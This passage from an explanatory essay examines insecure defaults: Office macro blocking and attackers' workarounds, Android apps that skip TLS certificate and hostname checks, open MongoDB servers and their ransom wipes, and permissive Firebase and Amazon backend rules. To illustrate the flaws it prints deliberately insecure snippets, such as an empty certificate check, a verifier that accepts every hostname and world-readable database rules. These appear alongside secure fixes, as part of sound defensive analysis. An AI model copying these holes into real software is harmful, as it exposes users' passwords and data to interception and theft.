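| Links and PDF files | Too common in normal email to block | Attackers shifted to them in 2023 |

Attackers could get around the block with a disk image such as an ISO file, which packs a copy of a whole disk into one file. Windows marked the ISO file as downloaded but not the spreadsheet inside it, so Office treated the spreadsheet as a local file and offered the old button to enable macros. Attackers could also leave out the macro and put an ordinary program in the disk image.

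Proofpoint found that campaigns using shortcut files rose by 1,675% from October 2021 to June 2022, although an increase this large usually means there were very few at the start. Campaigns using disk images, archives or shortcut files rose by nearly 175% combined. In late 2022, archive files such as ZIP overtook Office documents as carriers of malware, according to BetaNews' *Archive files overtake Office docs as a malware delivery method*.

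Most of the replacements lasted only a few months. Microsoft blocked some of them, and IBM thinks better detection stopped others. Few people have a legitimate reason to email a disk image, so a mail filter can treat every one as suspicious, which it can't do with PDFs. Some criminals went back to a flaw in Office's equation editor that Microsoft had fixed in November 2017. It was the most common exploit in IBM's spam data for 2023, so attackers evidently still expected to find copies of Office that lacked the fix more than five years later.

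One group that had used macros almost exclusively tried up to six methods in a single month. In 2022, Check Point Research had hoped that the extra trouble and expense would persuade some small-time criminals to give up, but nobody seems to have measured whether any did.

### Whether fewer computers were infected

A fall in macro attacks does not necessarily mean a fall in infections. Barracuda's *AI storm on the cybersecurity horizon* (2024) reports that IBM recorded 44% fewer phishing attacks in 2023 than in 2022, and 12% fewer ransomware attacks on businesses. The macro block may have contributed to both declines. But IBM also describes a surge in attacks on identities, in which criminals log in with stolen passwords. Some attackers who stopped sending attachments may have found this method easier.

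Trend Micro's email filters detected 16 million known malware files in 2023, up 3,079%, and 3 million unknown ones, down 18%. The company attributes the drop in unknown files partly to the macro block. But the percentages imply that total detections rose from roughly 4 million to 19 million. These counts include only files the company caught, so they don't show how many others reached a victim.

The Center for Internet Security's *Top 10 Malware Q4 2025* (2026) reports that malware notifications rose 7% from the previous quarter. SocGholish, which spreads through fake browser updates on hacked websites, accounted for 30% of the detections. A rise over one quarter in late 2025 can't show how the 2022 default affected total malware either, but the SocGholish detections show that malware was still spreading without macros.

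Office files have remained a small share of threats. HP Wolf Security (2026) examined threats that reached its customers' computers in the first quarter of 2026. Documents such as Word files made up 7% and spreadsheets 4%, compared with 39% for programs and scripts. Some of the Office files probably relied on software flaws instead of macros, so the share that used macros may be even smaller.

Macro attacks continue. HP Wolf Security (2025) describes fake purchase orders sent to Chinese-speaking organizations, and says such attacks exploit badly configured systems. In early 2026, another group sent Spanish-speaking users, mainly in Central America, a spreadsheet with a blurred bank statement and a request to enable content. The request can still work where an organization has turned off the block or the file has lost its Mark of the Web.

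Other attackers make a similar request without using Office, so a default setting in Office can't stop them. In an attack called ClickFix, a website shows a fake test of whether the visitor is human. The page copies a command to the clipboard and tells the visitor to paste and run it in Windows.

The block therefore closed one easy and popular route, but nobody has shown that it reduced the total number of infections. There might have been more infections without it, since criminals would have kept using macros alongside their newer methods, but we can't test this with the available counts.

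### Why it took 27 years

The delay came even though virus researchers had foreseen the threat. They had discussed macro viruses in the 1980s, according to O'Reilly's *Macro Viruses*, and were puzzled that none had appeared in the popular office programs of the time. After Concept, the security industry spent years asking Microsoft to let customers switch macros off completely or install Office without them.

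Ducklin, who admits to simplifying, says Microsoft left macros on by default for commercial reasons. Reviewers and customers judge a program by what it does when first installed, and competitors could portray Office without macros as a cheap product. The vast majority of users did not need macros, but influential customers expected them. A company whose invoicing depended on a macro would complain as soon as it stopped working, while a home user with an infected computer was unlikely to blame a default setting.

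Until Windows began to mark downloaded files in 2004, Office had no good way to block macros from strangers without also blocking legitimate ones, such as an accountant's. The marking made this technical obstacle much smaller. By 2016 Microsoft had built the block and was offering it to large customers. It also turned the block on by default for Office on Windows 10 S, a restricted edition that runs only apps from Microsoft's store (Microsoft's *Block suspicious macros in Office on Windows 10 S*). So for at least the last six years of the delay, Microsoft was choosing whose work to disrupt.

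Before 2022, much of the burden of malicious macros fell on people who had never written a macro. Home users and small firms had the least protection because they had no administrator to set a policy. Blocking macros by default moved some of the burden to organizations that use them. Their administrators now have to find out which departments depend on macros, ask suppliers to sign their code and decide which folders to trust.

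Blocking by default also made it harder for novices to share their macros. The clerk's report still works from a folder her company trusts, but if she emails it to a customer, Office blocks the macro. She can get a certificate and ask the customer to trust it, or explain how to open the file's properties and tick "Unblock", which is also what a criminal would tell the customer to do.

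## Android apps that failed to check encrypted connections

Android had a safe default for encrypted connections from the beginning, whereas Office had no safe default against macros from strangers until 2022. Android checked that an app was talking to the right server even if the developer wrote no security code. Many developers, novices and professionals alike, pasted in a few lines of code that turned this check off, often because the check had stopped their app from working during a test.

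### How an app recognizes its server

Suppose the guestbook from the first section gets an Android app, and its owner logs in from a café. The app connects over HTTPS, which encrypts the traffic with a protocol called TLS (formerly SSL). This keeps other customers from reading the password, but only if the app's encryption key is shared with the guestbook's server, not an impostor.

The server starts by sending a certificate, a small file that contains the site's name, a public key and the signature of a certificate authority. A certificate authority is an organization that confirms who controls the name. The server must also prove that it holds the matching private key, so an attacker cannot impersonate the site just by copying its certificate. The app checks that the signature leads back to an authority on Android's built-in list, that the certificate has not expired, and that it names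 the site the app requested.

An attacker can set up a Wi-Fi hotspot with the café's name and answer in place of the server. Making a certificate with the guestbook's name on it takes a minute, but no recognized authority will sign it, so Android breaks off the connection. The attack works if the app contains something like this:

```
new X509TrustManager() {
    public void checkServerTrusted(X509Certificate[] chain,
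                                   String authType) {
        // nothing here
    }
    ...
}
```

Android passes the server's certificate to `checkServerTrusted`, which should raise an error if the certificate is invalid. An empty method never raises an error, so the app accepts every certificate. An attacker who intercepts the connection can therefore present their own certificate, and the app will encrypt the password with a key that the attacker knows. The attacker reads the password, encrypts it again and forwards it to the real server, then relays the server's reply to the app. The guestbook still works during this man-in-the-middle attack, so its owner sees nothing wrong.

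Another common mistake is to check the signature but not the name:

```
public boolean verify(String hostname, SSLSession session) {
    return true;
}
```

The attacker now needs a genuine certificate, but it can be for any website, including the attacker's own.

Ordinary tests don't reveal either mistake. *Rethinking SSL Development in an Appified World* (Fahl, Harbach and colleagues, 2013) quotes a developer who checked the researchers' warning by connecting a phone to a laptop's hotspot and recording the traffic. The recording contained only encrypted data, and the developer concluded, "So I really cannot see what the problem is here." The test missed the flaw because the laptop only recorded traffic, when it would have had to pose as the server to expose the problem.

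### How many apps had the flaw

Fahl's group had published the first large count in 2012. They searched 13,500 popular free Android apps and found code in 1,074 of them, or 8%, that accepted any certificate or any name. In Threatpost's *Research Shows Serious Problems With Android App SSL Implementations*, the security researcher Jon Oberheide objected that such code may never run, for example because many developers use it only in a test mode.

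The group had also attacked 100 selected apps by hand and intercepted data from 41 of them. The apps with confirmed flaws had between 40 million and 185 million users in total. Because the researchers had picked these apps, the result can't be used to estimate the share of vulnerable apps across Google Play. *Why Eve and Mallory Still Love Android* (Oltrogge, Huaman and colleagues, 2020) summarizes a 2014 survey that gives a better idea of how much Oberheide's objection matters. The survey flagged 1,453 of 23,418 apps as potentially vulnerable and confirmed the flaw in 726, so a search of the code may overstate the problem by about a factor of two.

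Apple reviewed apps more strictly than Google, but this made little difference. Fahl and colleagues installed 1,009 popular free apps on an iPhone and attacked their connections. Of the 697 apps that used encryption, 98 (14%) let the researchers read sensitive data. Another 82 sent such data unencrypted. The 14% isn't directly comparable with Android's 8%, because it leaves out apps without encrypted traffic. The 98 apps were 9.7% of all those tested.

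No one seems to have counted successful attacks. An attacker has to be on the victim's network, or somewhere else along the route, and can't search Google for victims as the Santy worm did. Probably far fewer people lost passwords this way than had a vulnerable app.

### Mistakes in the encryption itself

Developers also had to encrypt data themselves, for example when an app stored passwords on the phone. Egele, Brumley and colleagues (2013), in *An Empirical Study of Cryptographic Misuse in Android Applications*, downloaded 145,095 apps and looked for six basic mistakes. They were able to analyze 11,748 apps that used cryptography outside a few common libraries. Of these, 10,327 (88%) contained at least one mistake.

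Here the default was part of the problem. A developer who asked Android for the respected encryption method AES wrote:

`Cipher.getInstance("AES")`

AES encrypts data in blocks of 16 bytes, and there are several ways to apply it to longer text. If the developer didn't choose one, Android used ECB, which encrypts each block separately, so identical blocks look identical after encryption. Someone who sees a list of encrypted passwords can therefore tell which ones are the same. The study found ECB in 7,656 apps, and in 5,656 of them the developer had accepted the default. A different default would have prevented this mistake in almost half of the apps studied, although many of them made other mistakes too.

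The next most common mistake, in 3,644 apps, was to write the encryption key into the app, where anyone who downloads the app can find it. One game with over 50 million installations encrypted its messages to the server with such a key, and Egele and colleagues easily decrypted them.

Breaking a rule of cryptography doesn't always give an attacker a way in. Help Net Security's *Popular Android apps are rife with cryptographic vulnerabilities* describes a later project in which researchers took apart 28 flagged apps and found that 14 were open to attack, in some cases only if the attacker had already gained extra rights on the phone. But the mistakes themselves remained common. In August 2021 A-SIT's *Automatic Detection and Mitigation of Crypto API Misuse in Android Applications* (2021) concluded that Google's efforts had brought no substantial improvement. (A-SIT, an Austrian security center,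 was presenting its own solution.)

### Why developers turned the check off

Fahl's group wrote to 78 developers of vulnerable Android and iPhone apps, and 14 agreed to an interview. Five of the 14 had turned off the certificate check so that their app could connect to a test server. Certificates from a recognized authority cost money then, so developers commonly gave test servers self-signed certificates, which a server's owner can make for free. Android correctly rejects these, so the five developers added code to accept every certificate and forgot to remove it before release.

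Other developers wanted to keep a self-signed certificate permanently. One had copied code from a forum and remembered only that it "makes self-signed certificates work". Another knew that a few users ran blogs with self-signed certificates. Android had no built-in warning that would let those users decide whether to trust a certificate, so the developer made the app accept every certificate for all users. Some iPhone developers wrote no unsafe code themselves but relied on a popular library that turned off certificate checks by default.

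Developers could use a self-signed certificate safely by programming the app to accept only that certificate, a technique called pinning. But the wrong solution, accepting all certificates, was easier to find. On Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers, threads about accepting all certificates had more than 30,000 views, while those about pinning had fewer than 600.

Three months after the warning, only 21 of the 78 developers had fixed the flaw, 51 had not, and the other six apps had disappeared from the stores. Nine of the 14 interviewed developers fixed it, compared with 12 of the other 64. Personal help may explain the difference, but developers who agree to an interview are probably also more willing to repair their apps.

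Some developers tried to fix the problem but got it wrong. One started checking the name in the certificate but still accepted self-signed certificates, in which an attacker can write any name. The company behind an online banking app needed two attempts to fix it, even though the researchers had sent it the code.

### Code from Stack Overflow

*Stack Overflow Considered Harmful?* (Fischer, Böttinger and colleagues, 2017) examined how much unsafe code came from Stack Overflow. The researchers collected about 4,000 security-related snippets from the site's Android discussions, labelled 1,360 of them by hand as secure or insecure, and trained a program to classify the rest. They then searched 1,305,820 free apps for code with the same structure.

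They found matches in 200,672 apps, or 15.4%, and 97.9% of these apps contained at least one insecure snippet. Both figures depend heavily on one snippet, the empty certificate check, which appeared in 180,388 apps. All the other insecure snippets together appeared in 43,941.

An empty check is also poor evidence of copying, because it has no content to compare. The researchers recognized it by its method names, which Android prescribes, so a developer who wrote one without ever visiting Stack Overflow would have produced the same match. Fischer and colleagues acknowledge that they can't prove where any of the code came from, though they think Stack Overflow is very likely the source. The count still shows that an enormous number of apps contained the empty check.

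The search found secure code for TLS connections in only 441 apps, compared with 183,268 that had an insecure snippet. These counts make the problem look worse than it is, because an app that leaves Android's built-in check alone needs no copied code for the search to find.

Warnings in the comments didn't stop people from copying insecure code. The empty check had warnings beneath it, and insecure snippets with warnings appeared in apps more often than those without. This is probably because popular snippets are copied more and also get more comments.

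Novices couldn't rely on Stack Overflow votes either. *How Reliable is the Crowdsourced Knowledge of Security Implementation?* (Fischer, Wang and colleagues, 2019) examined answers containing Java code that appeared on the site more than once. Of 505 answers about TLS, 355 (70%) were insecure. Across all the security topics in the study, insecure answers had an average score of 14, compared with 5 for secure ones, and received about twice as many views. Of 72 answers by the site's most trusted users, 26 were insecure. People vote for answers that solve their problem, and accepting every certificate removes the error message.

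Careless developers may simply prefer Stack Overflow to the official documentation, so none of this shows that the site made anyone's code worse. In 2016, Yasemin Acar and colleagues tested whether it does by assigning developers their source of help. They gave 54 Android developers, both students and professionals, security-related programming tasks. Some could use only Stack Overflow, some only Android's official documentation, some only books, and the rest whatever they liked. According to the University of Maryland, where part of the team worked, the Stack Overflow group wrote less secure code than the documentation group. But Fischer and colleagues note that the documentation group's code worked less often, and that the Stack Overflow group produced the most working code. That would probably draw a novice with a deadline back to Stack Overflow.

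Later experiments tried to make secure code as easy to find as insecure code. In 2019, researchers including Felix Fischer tested a version of Stack Overflow that warned about insecure cryptographic snippets and recommended secure ones for the same purpose. It had secure alternatives for 99.37% of the insecure snippets, and developers who got the advice did better on common tasks. A 2021 experiment used no warnings and instead reordered Google's search results so that pages with secure code came first. In Google's usual order, there was at least a 22.8% chance that one of the top three results led to insecure code. Participants who got the new order submitted more secure solutions, and they didn't need to know anything about security to benefit. Both experiments dealt with encrypting data, so they didn't measure how many developers would have left Android's certificate check in place.

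### Fandango and Credit Karma

Companies first faced consequences in March 2014, when the US Federal Trade Commission (FTC) announced settlements with Fandango, which sells movie tickets, and Credit Karma, which shows people their credit scores. Both had told customers that their apps protected personal data, but the apps accepted any certificate.

Fandango's iPhone app failed to check its encrypted connections for nearly four years, while customers used it to send their credit card numbers. When a security researcher reported the flaw through a customer service form, the company's system misclassified the message as a password problem and sent an automatic reply. Credit Karma let the company that built its iPhone app turn off the check for testing, and nobody made sure it was back on in the finished version. Credit Karma fixed the flaw after a user pointed it out, but a month later it released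 an Android app with the same flaw.

The settlements included no fine, but both companies had to set up security programs and submit to outside assessments every two years for 20 years. Such a case can make a large company test its apps, but it would do little about a hobbyist's app. The FTC could hardly investigate thousands of developers one by one, and the charges relied on promises about security that a hobbyist may never have made.

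### Google Play's scanner

From 2014, Google scanned apps on Google Play for known security problems, warned their developers and set a deadline for fixing them. Developers who missed the deadline usually couldn't publish an update until they fixed the problem, but the existing version stayed in the store. In 2019 Google said the program had helped more than 300,000 developers fix over a million apps.

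That total covers every kind of problem the scanner looked for, including outdated copies of OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library. According to OWASP's *Android Network Communication*, an outdated copy has been a reason for rejection since July 2016. A scanner can recognize an old library fairly easily by its version, but a missing certificate check is harder to detect because developers can write the faulty code in many ways.

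Google's measures against unsafe connections, as Oltrogge and colleagues list them, came in this order:

| Date | Change |
|---|---|
| May 2016 | Google Play starts rejecting apps with unsafe certificate checks |
| August 2016 | Android 7 lets developers use a settings file instead of code |
| November 2016 | Google Play starts rejecting apps that ignore certificate errors in web pages they display |
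| March 2017 | Google Play starts rejecting apps that don't check the server's name properly |
| August 2018 | Android 9 blocks unencrypted connections by default |
| November 2019 | Google Play requires updates of existing apps to follow the Android 9 rules |

To test the scanner, Oltrogge and colleagues posed as a well-meaning developer who had left unsafe code in an app. They submitted 18 versions with different mistakes, and Google Play accepted 16. It let through the empty certificate check from the beginning of this section, even after the researchers had renamed it `TrustAllTrustManager`. It also accepted code that approved any server name. It did block an app that ignored every certificate error in a web page, but not when the same code was behind a switch for testing. (The researchers removed each accepted app at once, and nobody had installed any of them.)

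Google Play announced a ban on the empty check in 2016 but still accepted apps that used it about four years later. Some developers had complained online about rejected apps, so the scanner evidently caught some, but a few of the complaints concerned libraries that passed when the researchers tried them. A developer who gets a warning can also make small changes until the warning disappears, without making the app any safer.

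Oltrogge and colleagues also ran a code scanner on 15,000 apps from Google Play and found unsafe certificate or name checks in 5,511 (36.7%). They consider this in line with the findings from 2012. It is more than four times the 8% that Fahl's group found, but the two figures aren't directly comparable, because the newer tool also scanned libraries that came with the app and couldn't tell whether the code ever ran. By contrast, according to Oltrogge and colleagues' summary, *Studying TLS Usage in Android Apps* (Razaghpanah, Akhavan Niaki and colleagues, 2017) observed the connections of 7,258 apps on people's phones and found that only 2% used their own certificate checks. The share of apps that an attacker could have exploited around 2020 is therefore uncertain, but apps with unsafe code were clearly still getting into Google Play.

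### Settings instead of code

Fahl and colleagues had argued in 2013 that it was useless to educate developers or simplify the libraries, because most developers just wanted their connection to work. They proposed that Android should do all the checking itself and let developers adjust it through settings. With Android 7, Google adopted much of this idea. A developer with a self-signed test server could now write:

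```
<network-security-config>
    <debug-overrides>
        <trust-anchors>
            <certificates src="@raw/test_server" />
        </trust-anchors>
    </debug-overrides>
</network-security-config>
```

These settings make the app accept the test server's certificate, but only in the version the developer uses for testing. Google Play doesn't accept test versions, so a developer who forgets to remove the settings puts nobody at risk. The settings would have solved the problem for the five developers who forgot to restore the check. By 2020, 10,085 apps contained settings of this kind.

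But Google left the old method in place. Fahl's group had wanted to stop apps from replacing Android's check with their own, and had tested a version of Android that did this. In Google's version, an empty `checkServerTrusted` still works and can override the settings file. A novice who follows an answer from 2012 will therefore still get an app that connects to the test server but will also connect to any attacker's server.

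The settings file also made pinning much easier, since developers no longer had to program it. But Oltrogge and colleagues found pinning in only 663 apps, less than 1% of those with a settings file, and in some of them the pin was an empty string or an obvious placeholder. Complicated code was apparently not the only thing that had put developers off pinning.

### Unencrypted traffic after Android 9

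Some apps didn't encrypt their connections at all, so an attacker didn't even need to make a certificate. Android 9 blocked unencrypted connections by default, though developers could still allow them. Every app states which version of Android it targets, and the new default applied only to apps that targeted Android 9 or higher, so older apps kept working. Google Play then stopped accepting new apps and updates that targeted an earlier version. As a result, the new default reached existing apps when their developers next updated them, whereas PHP's new default hadn't reached servers that kept their old settings.

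At the end of 2019, Google (2019) reported that 80% of Android apps were encrypting traffic by default, as were 90% of those that targeted Android 9 or higher. Some of this would have happened without Android 9. Razaghpanah and colleagues cite Google figures showing that the encrypted share of connections to Google's servers rose from 50% to 85% between January 2014 and April 2017, before Android 9 existed. An app can encrypt its traffic only if the server supports it, and by 2018 far more servers did.

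Oltrogge and colleagues got a less favorable result from a collection of 1.3 million free apps that ended in March 2020. Of these, 565,910 targeted Android 9 or higher, and 174,369 of them allowed unencrypted traffic to every server with one line in the app's main configuration file:

`android:usesCleartextTraffic="true"`

This is 31%, three times what Google's figure implies. Another 84,060 apps used the newer settings file to allow unencrypted traffic, usually also to every server. The two samples were different, and timing may also explain some of the gap. Developers who adopted Android 9 early probably had apps that already used encryption. Those who waited for the November 2019 deadline had more reason to turn the default off, and Google's count came too early to include many of them.

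The study's best-known result is that 88.87% of apps with their own settings file had weakened Android's protection. But developers who are satisfied with the default don't need such a file, and only about 7% of the apps had one. The result shows what developers use the file for, but it is weak evidence of how safe the average app is.

Turning off the default was often unnecessary. The study found that 8,935 apps exempted a server from encryption even though the server supported it. In most cases, the server redirected visitors to the encrypted address. The developers could have solved the problem by changing `http` to `https` in their apps.

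As with Django's CSRF token, a developer who searches for the error message finds the line that turns the protection off. Google (2019) described any remaining unencrypted connection as "the result of an explicit choice by the developer". The developer does have to change the setting, but a novice who pastes in a line to clear an error may not understand what it does.

To see what apps were sending without encryption, Oltrogge and colleagues recorded the traffic of 20 randomly chosen apps that had turned off the default. Thirteen sent user data, mostly for advertising and tracking, but a school app and an app for controlling front-door devices also sent usernames and passwords. Of 20 more apps chosen because they were likely to handle sensitive data, 11 sent login details. Anyone on the same Wi-Fi could have read these passwords with a free program. The samples were small, and the second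 was not random.

Some experienced developers also turned off the default. WhatsApp, YouTube and Gmail had settings that permitted unencrypted traffic, and popular apps were more likely than obscure ones to have a settings file. A large company may have a good reason for an exception and staff to monitor it.

Smaller developers often allowed unencrypted traffic in their apps because of someone else's code. Many free apps earn money through an advertising library, and the ads may come from servers that don't use encryption. The documentation for one such library, MoPub, included instructions to allow unencrypted traffic everywhere and a settings file to copy. The file blocked unencrypted traffic only to `example.com`, a placeholder that developers were supposed to replace with their own server's address. Oltrogge and colleagues found the file in 1,609 apps. In the cases they describe, the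 developers had copied it unchanged, so their apps could still connect to their own servers without encryption.

The settings apply to the whole app, and a developer can't list every server that an ad might come from. Other researchers have proposed separate rules for each library, which would let an ad load without encryption while still requiring it for the login form next to it.

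## Databases and app backends left open to the internet

An encrypted connection protects a password only on its way to the server. If anyone on the internet can read the database that stores the password, an attacker can get it without intercepting traffic on a café's Wi-Fi.

In the PHP guestbook from the first section, visitors sent requests to a program on the server, and only that program accessed the database. In the 2010s, many novices put databases online that strangers could access directly.

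### MongoDB without a password

MongoDB, first released in 2009, appealed to beginners because they could store records without designing tables first. Early versions came with no password and accepted connections from every network the computer was on. Rapid7's *The Ransomware Chronicles* (2017) explains that such databases came with open settings to make them easy to try. This did little harm on a laptop behind a home router, but a rented cloud server has a public address, and anyone who connected to MongoDB there could read, change or delete everything.

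One line in the settings closes the database to outsiders:

`bind_ip = 127.0.0.1`

A computer uses the address 127.0.0.1 for itself, so MongoDB now accepts connections only from programs on the same machine, such as the guestbook. The database still has no password, but strangers can no longer connect to it.

Roman Shtylman raised the problem with MongoDB's developers in February 2012. Shodan, a search engine for servers and devices connected to the internet, reports in *It's the Data, Stupid!* that they took a little over two years to change the default. MongoDB's release notes show that the change, made in version 2.6 in 2014, covered only the official packages for common types of Linux. Other downloads stayed open by default until version 3.6, at the end of 2017.

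### The ransom attacks of January 2017

In January 2017 the researcher Victor Gevers searched for open MongoDB servers and found many databases with names like "readme" and "readplease", each containing a single file with a demand for payment. On January 10, KrebsOnSecurity (2017), a security news site, reported that more than 52,000 MongoDB databases were publicly accessible and that at least 29,000 were gone.

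The attackers looked up open MongoDB servers on Shodan, connected without a password and deleted the data, sometimes after copying it. They didn't need a flaw in MongoDB's code. Several groups did this at once and replaced each other's ransom notes, so victims often couldn't tell who had their data, if anyone did. Hardly anyone who paid got their data back. Niall Merrigan, who was helping victims in his spare time, told those who still wanted to pay to ask first for one or two files as proof that the attackers had the data.

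Later that month Rapid7 found about 56,000 MongoDB servers online, half of them held to ransom. The same had happened to 58% of roughly 18,000 servers running Elasticsearch, another database with open default settings. These attacks were unusually easy to count because the attackers left a note that anyone could read. The count overstates the loss, since some of the databases held only test data.

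### How long the servers stayed open

Several organizations have counted MongoDB servers that anyone could use. The first figure below is from Saarland University, as reported by van Scheppingen of the database company Severalnines, and the next three are from Shodan. Cyclonis' *One Hacker Wiped Data From Nearly Half of All MongoDB Databases* reports the 2020 figure, which is from Shadowserver, a nonprofit that scans the internet. Morag's *MongoDB Ransom Isn't Back* (2026) gives the last figure, also based on Shodan's data.

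| Date | Open MongoDB servers |
|---|---|
| Early 2015 | about 40,000 |
| July 2015 | nearly 30,000 |
| December 2015 | at least 35,000 |
| January 2017 | over 52,000 |
| July 2020 | about 23,000 |
| January 2026 | 3,100 |

The number of open servers was still rising more than two years after the first change of default, partly because of old installations. In July 2015, 40% of the open servers ran version 1.8.1, which dated from 2011. By December that version was no longer among the five most common, so a few large owners may have run most of those servers. But Shodan's *It's Still the Data, Stupid!* found that month that the most common version on open servers was 3.0.7, a recent release whose official packages had the safe default. Some owners must have changed the setting. Others had probably upgraded and kept their old settings file, as many PHP users did with register_globals.

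By 2026 the number of open MongoDB servers had fallen by 94% from the 2017 figure. Morag found more than 200,000 servers visible online, of which only about 1.5% were open. The safe default in version 3.6 probably contributed a lot, but the ransom attacks also gave owners a strong reason to close their servers, and MongoDB had begun to offer a hosted version with secure settings. The fall took years. In the summer of 2020, more than two years after version 3.6 came out, a single attacker's script wiped about 23,000 databases.

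Some owners didn't realize they were reopening the database. According to a ticket in MongoDB's bug tracker, the company's instructions told people how to reopen the network but didn't warn them to set a password first. In Ottenheimer's *New MongoDB 3.6 Security Features*, however, the company's technology chief, Eliot Horowitz, says that anyone who turns on networking without a password has to do so "consciously".

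An experienced developer could also expose a database by accident, as happened at the news reader NewsBlur. NewsBlur moved its database into a Docker container, a package that runs a program separately from the rest of the computer. According to Ayende's *Yes, the network is hostile, even yours*, the move opened the MongoDB database to the internet, apparently because of a Docker default setting. An attacker then held the data to ransom.

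Many people also download containers that someone else has prepared. Morag found 763 on the public site Docker Hub that started MongoDB with `--bind_ip=0.0.0.0`, which makes the database accept connections from every network. A container with this setting is exposed only if its user opens the port to the outside. Most of the 763 had a few hundred downloads, but two had more than 15,000 each.

Attackers usually find open databases quickly. Morag put several online as bait, and all of them had ransom notes within days. Attackers had already wiped 1,416 of the 3,100 open servers. *The Hidden Ransomware Economy Running on Exposed Databases* (Paganini, 2026) reports a much higher rate from a five-year study, which found notes on 3,525 of 3,532 exposed MongoDB servers. But 3,532 is few for five years, since Shadowserver counted about 23,000 at one time. If the study found some servers because of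 their ransom notes, its rate would be too high. The attackers it traced had received about $753,000 for 30,515 databases, or $25 each, which can only be worthwhile because the attacks are almost entirely automated.

### One flaw in 60,314 apps

A ready-made container can spread one bad setting to thousands of users. Online app generators, which let people build phone apps from ready-made parts without writing code, could spread a flaw even further. *The Rise of the Citizen Developer* (Oltrogge, Derr and colleagues, 2018) examined 2,291,898 free apps from Google Play and traced at least 255,216 of them, or 11.1%, to such generators. The true share may be higher, because the count includes only apps from generators the researchers recognized.

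Oltrogge and colleagues studied 13 app generators in detail. Eleven put exactly the same code into every app, so two apps from the same generator differed only in a configuration file. The most popular of these, Seattle Cloud, had made 60,314 of the apps. Its code included a component that handled the app's internal files, which Seattle Cloud had mistakenly left open to other apps on the phone. A malicious app could use the component to read those files, including one that stored usernames and passwords for the app's login page. The researchers checked all 60,314 apps and found the component in every one. They found a similar flaw in 98.5% of the apps made with another generator, Mobincube.

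Six of the 13 generators also produced apps that accepted invalid certificates, the mistake described in the previous section. Oltrogge and colleagues conclude that the generators were making Android less safe overall. But they did not run the same tests on handwritten apps, and they acknowledge that ordinary developers make similar mistakes. The generators' customers might well have written less secure apps on their own.

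A generator can repair a flaw better than thousands of separate developers can. If Mobincube replaces its server's certificate, which had expired seven years before the study, every app that connects to the server benefits at once. A flaw in the shared code takes longer to fix, because the generator has to correct the code once, rebuild each app and publish it on Google Play, and users then have to install the update. Some generators publish apps for their customers, but others leave at least part of that work to the customers. Abandoned apps are another problem. Of 27,130 apps made with the paid generator Biznessapps, 5,137 had an expired license, and it is unclear who would update those. Oltrogge and colleagues were still reporting the flaws when they published, so their study can't show how many apps the generators repaired.

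### Apps without a server program

Other novices wrote their own app but used a hosted backend, such as Google's Firebase. These services supply a database, file storage and a login system, and the provider keeps the servers up to date. The developer doesn't need to install MongoDB or write any PHP, and the app sends its requests straight to the database.

In the PHP guestbook, the check that only the owner may delete a message runs on the server, where visitors can't tamper with it. In an app with a hosted backend, the developer's code runs on the user's phone. An attacker can take the database's address and key from the app and send requests directly, bypassing any checks in the app. The provider's server enforces access rules, but the developer has to write them.

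Zuo, Lin and Zhang write in *Why Does Your Data Leak?* (2019) that the security work left to developers who use a hosted backend is checking who users are and what they may do. They add that hosting makes attacks easier to repeat, because thousands of apps on Firebase accept the same requests. When every developer wrote a different server program, an attacker had to study each one.

"Why Does Your Data Leak?" examined 1,609,983 free Android apps downloaded in 2017 and found 107,081 that used the backends of Google, Amazon or Microsoft. The researchers tested these without reading anyone's data by requesting records that didn't exist. A server that replied that it couldn't find the record would have handed over a real one, while a properly protected server refused permission. The tests identified 15,098 apps with leaking backends. Ten of these apps had at least 100 million downloads each,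 so novices weren't the only ones responsible.

Some developers had put a master key in their apps. Amazon gives each customer a root key that gives access to everything in the account, and 569 of the 6,786 apps that used Amazon contained one. Microsoft's official sample code contained the equivalent mistake, so a beginner who carefully followed the documentation would have made it too. Microsoft corrected the sample after hearing from Zuo and colleagues.

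### Amazon's switch for public storage

Another 1,111 of the Amazon apps, or 16%, gave access to an entire storage area, which Amazon calls a bucket. New buckets were private, but owners could make them public by changing a setting or pasting in a rule. In 2018 Amazon added a switch, Block Public Access, that overrides such changes, and since April 2023 it has been on by default for every new bucket. An owner who wants a new bucket to be public now has to turn the switch off and then grant access.

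Nobody seems to have published a count of open buckets from before and after the change. It may have had only a modest effect on novices, because the switch was already on for buckets created through Amazon's website, where most beginners would start. Existing buckets also kept their old settings.

The switch would not necessarily have protected the 1,111 apps either. Zuo and colleagues had tested the buckets with keys taken from the apps, and Amazon treats a request with a valid key as coming from an authorized user. Blocking public access therefore doesn't help when every copy of an app contains a key with too many permissions.

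### Three Firebase rules

Firebase lets developers start a database in locked mode, which refuses every request, or in test mode, which accepts them all. The app doesn't work in locked mode until its developer has written some rules, so test mode is tempting. In their simplest form, the open rules are:

```
{
  "rules": {
    ".read": true,
    ".write": true
  }
}
```

With these rules, anyone who has the database's address can download or delete everything in it. Zuo and colleagues found that 6,380 of 101,380 Firebase apps (6.3%) had a database that anyone could read. Not all of these databases were left open by accident. Zuo and colleagues looked closely at 30 popular apps with leaking backends of all kinds and found that 26 exposed private data. One of the other four was a music quiz that stored only song details.

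Later scans still found many exposed databases. In 2020 the consumer website Comparitech examined about 155,000 Android apps that used Firebase and found that nearly 12,000, or between 7% and 8%, had publicly exposed databases. In 2024 three independent researchers checked more than five million web domains and found about 900 sites whose faulty Firebase rules exposed some 125 million user records. They wrote to most of the owners, and about a quarter fixed their rules.

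Google now makes the test rules expire after 30 days, which protects databases that their developers have forgotten. But a live app that still uses them will suddenly stop working, and the developer's quickest fix is to enter a later date, which leaves the database open.

A slightly more careful developer might replace `true` with a condition:

`".read": "auth != null"`

If a database admits any logged-in user and anyone can create an account, as in many apps, every user can read everyone else's data. Zuo and colleagues could test for this only in the 13,506 apps where their software could register an account automatically. In 9,023 of them, or two thirds, an ordinary user could read the whole database. Some of these databases may also have been open to people without accounts, and apps that accept automatic registration may not be typical. Even so, this mistake was probably far more common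 than leaving the database open to everyone.

If each user of the guestbook app has a folder of private messages, the correct rules are:

```
{
  "rules": {
    "messages": {
      "$uid": {
        ".read": "$uid === auth.uid",
        ".write": "$uid === auth.uid"
      }
    }
  }
}
```

Here `$uid` is a folder's name and `auth.uid` is the logged-in user's ID, so users can open only the folder named after their own ID. The developer also has to delete the old rules, because in Firebase a permission granted at the top applies to everything below it.

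The same rule can be wrong for other data. If it also covered user profiles with an administrator field, users could make themselves administrators, as in Rails before 2012.

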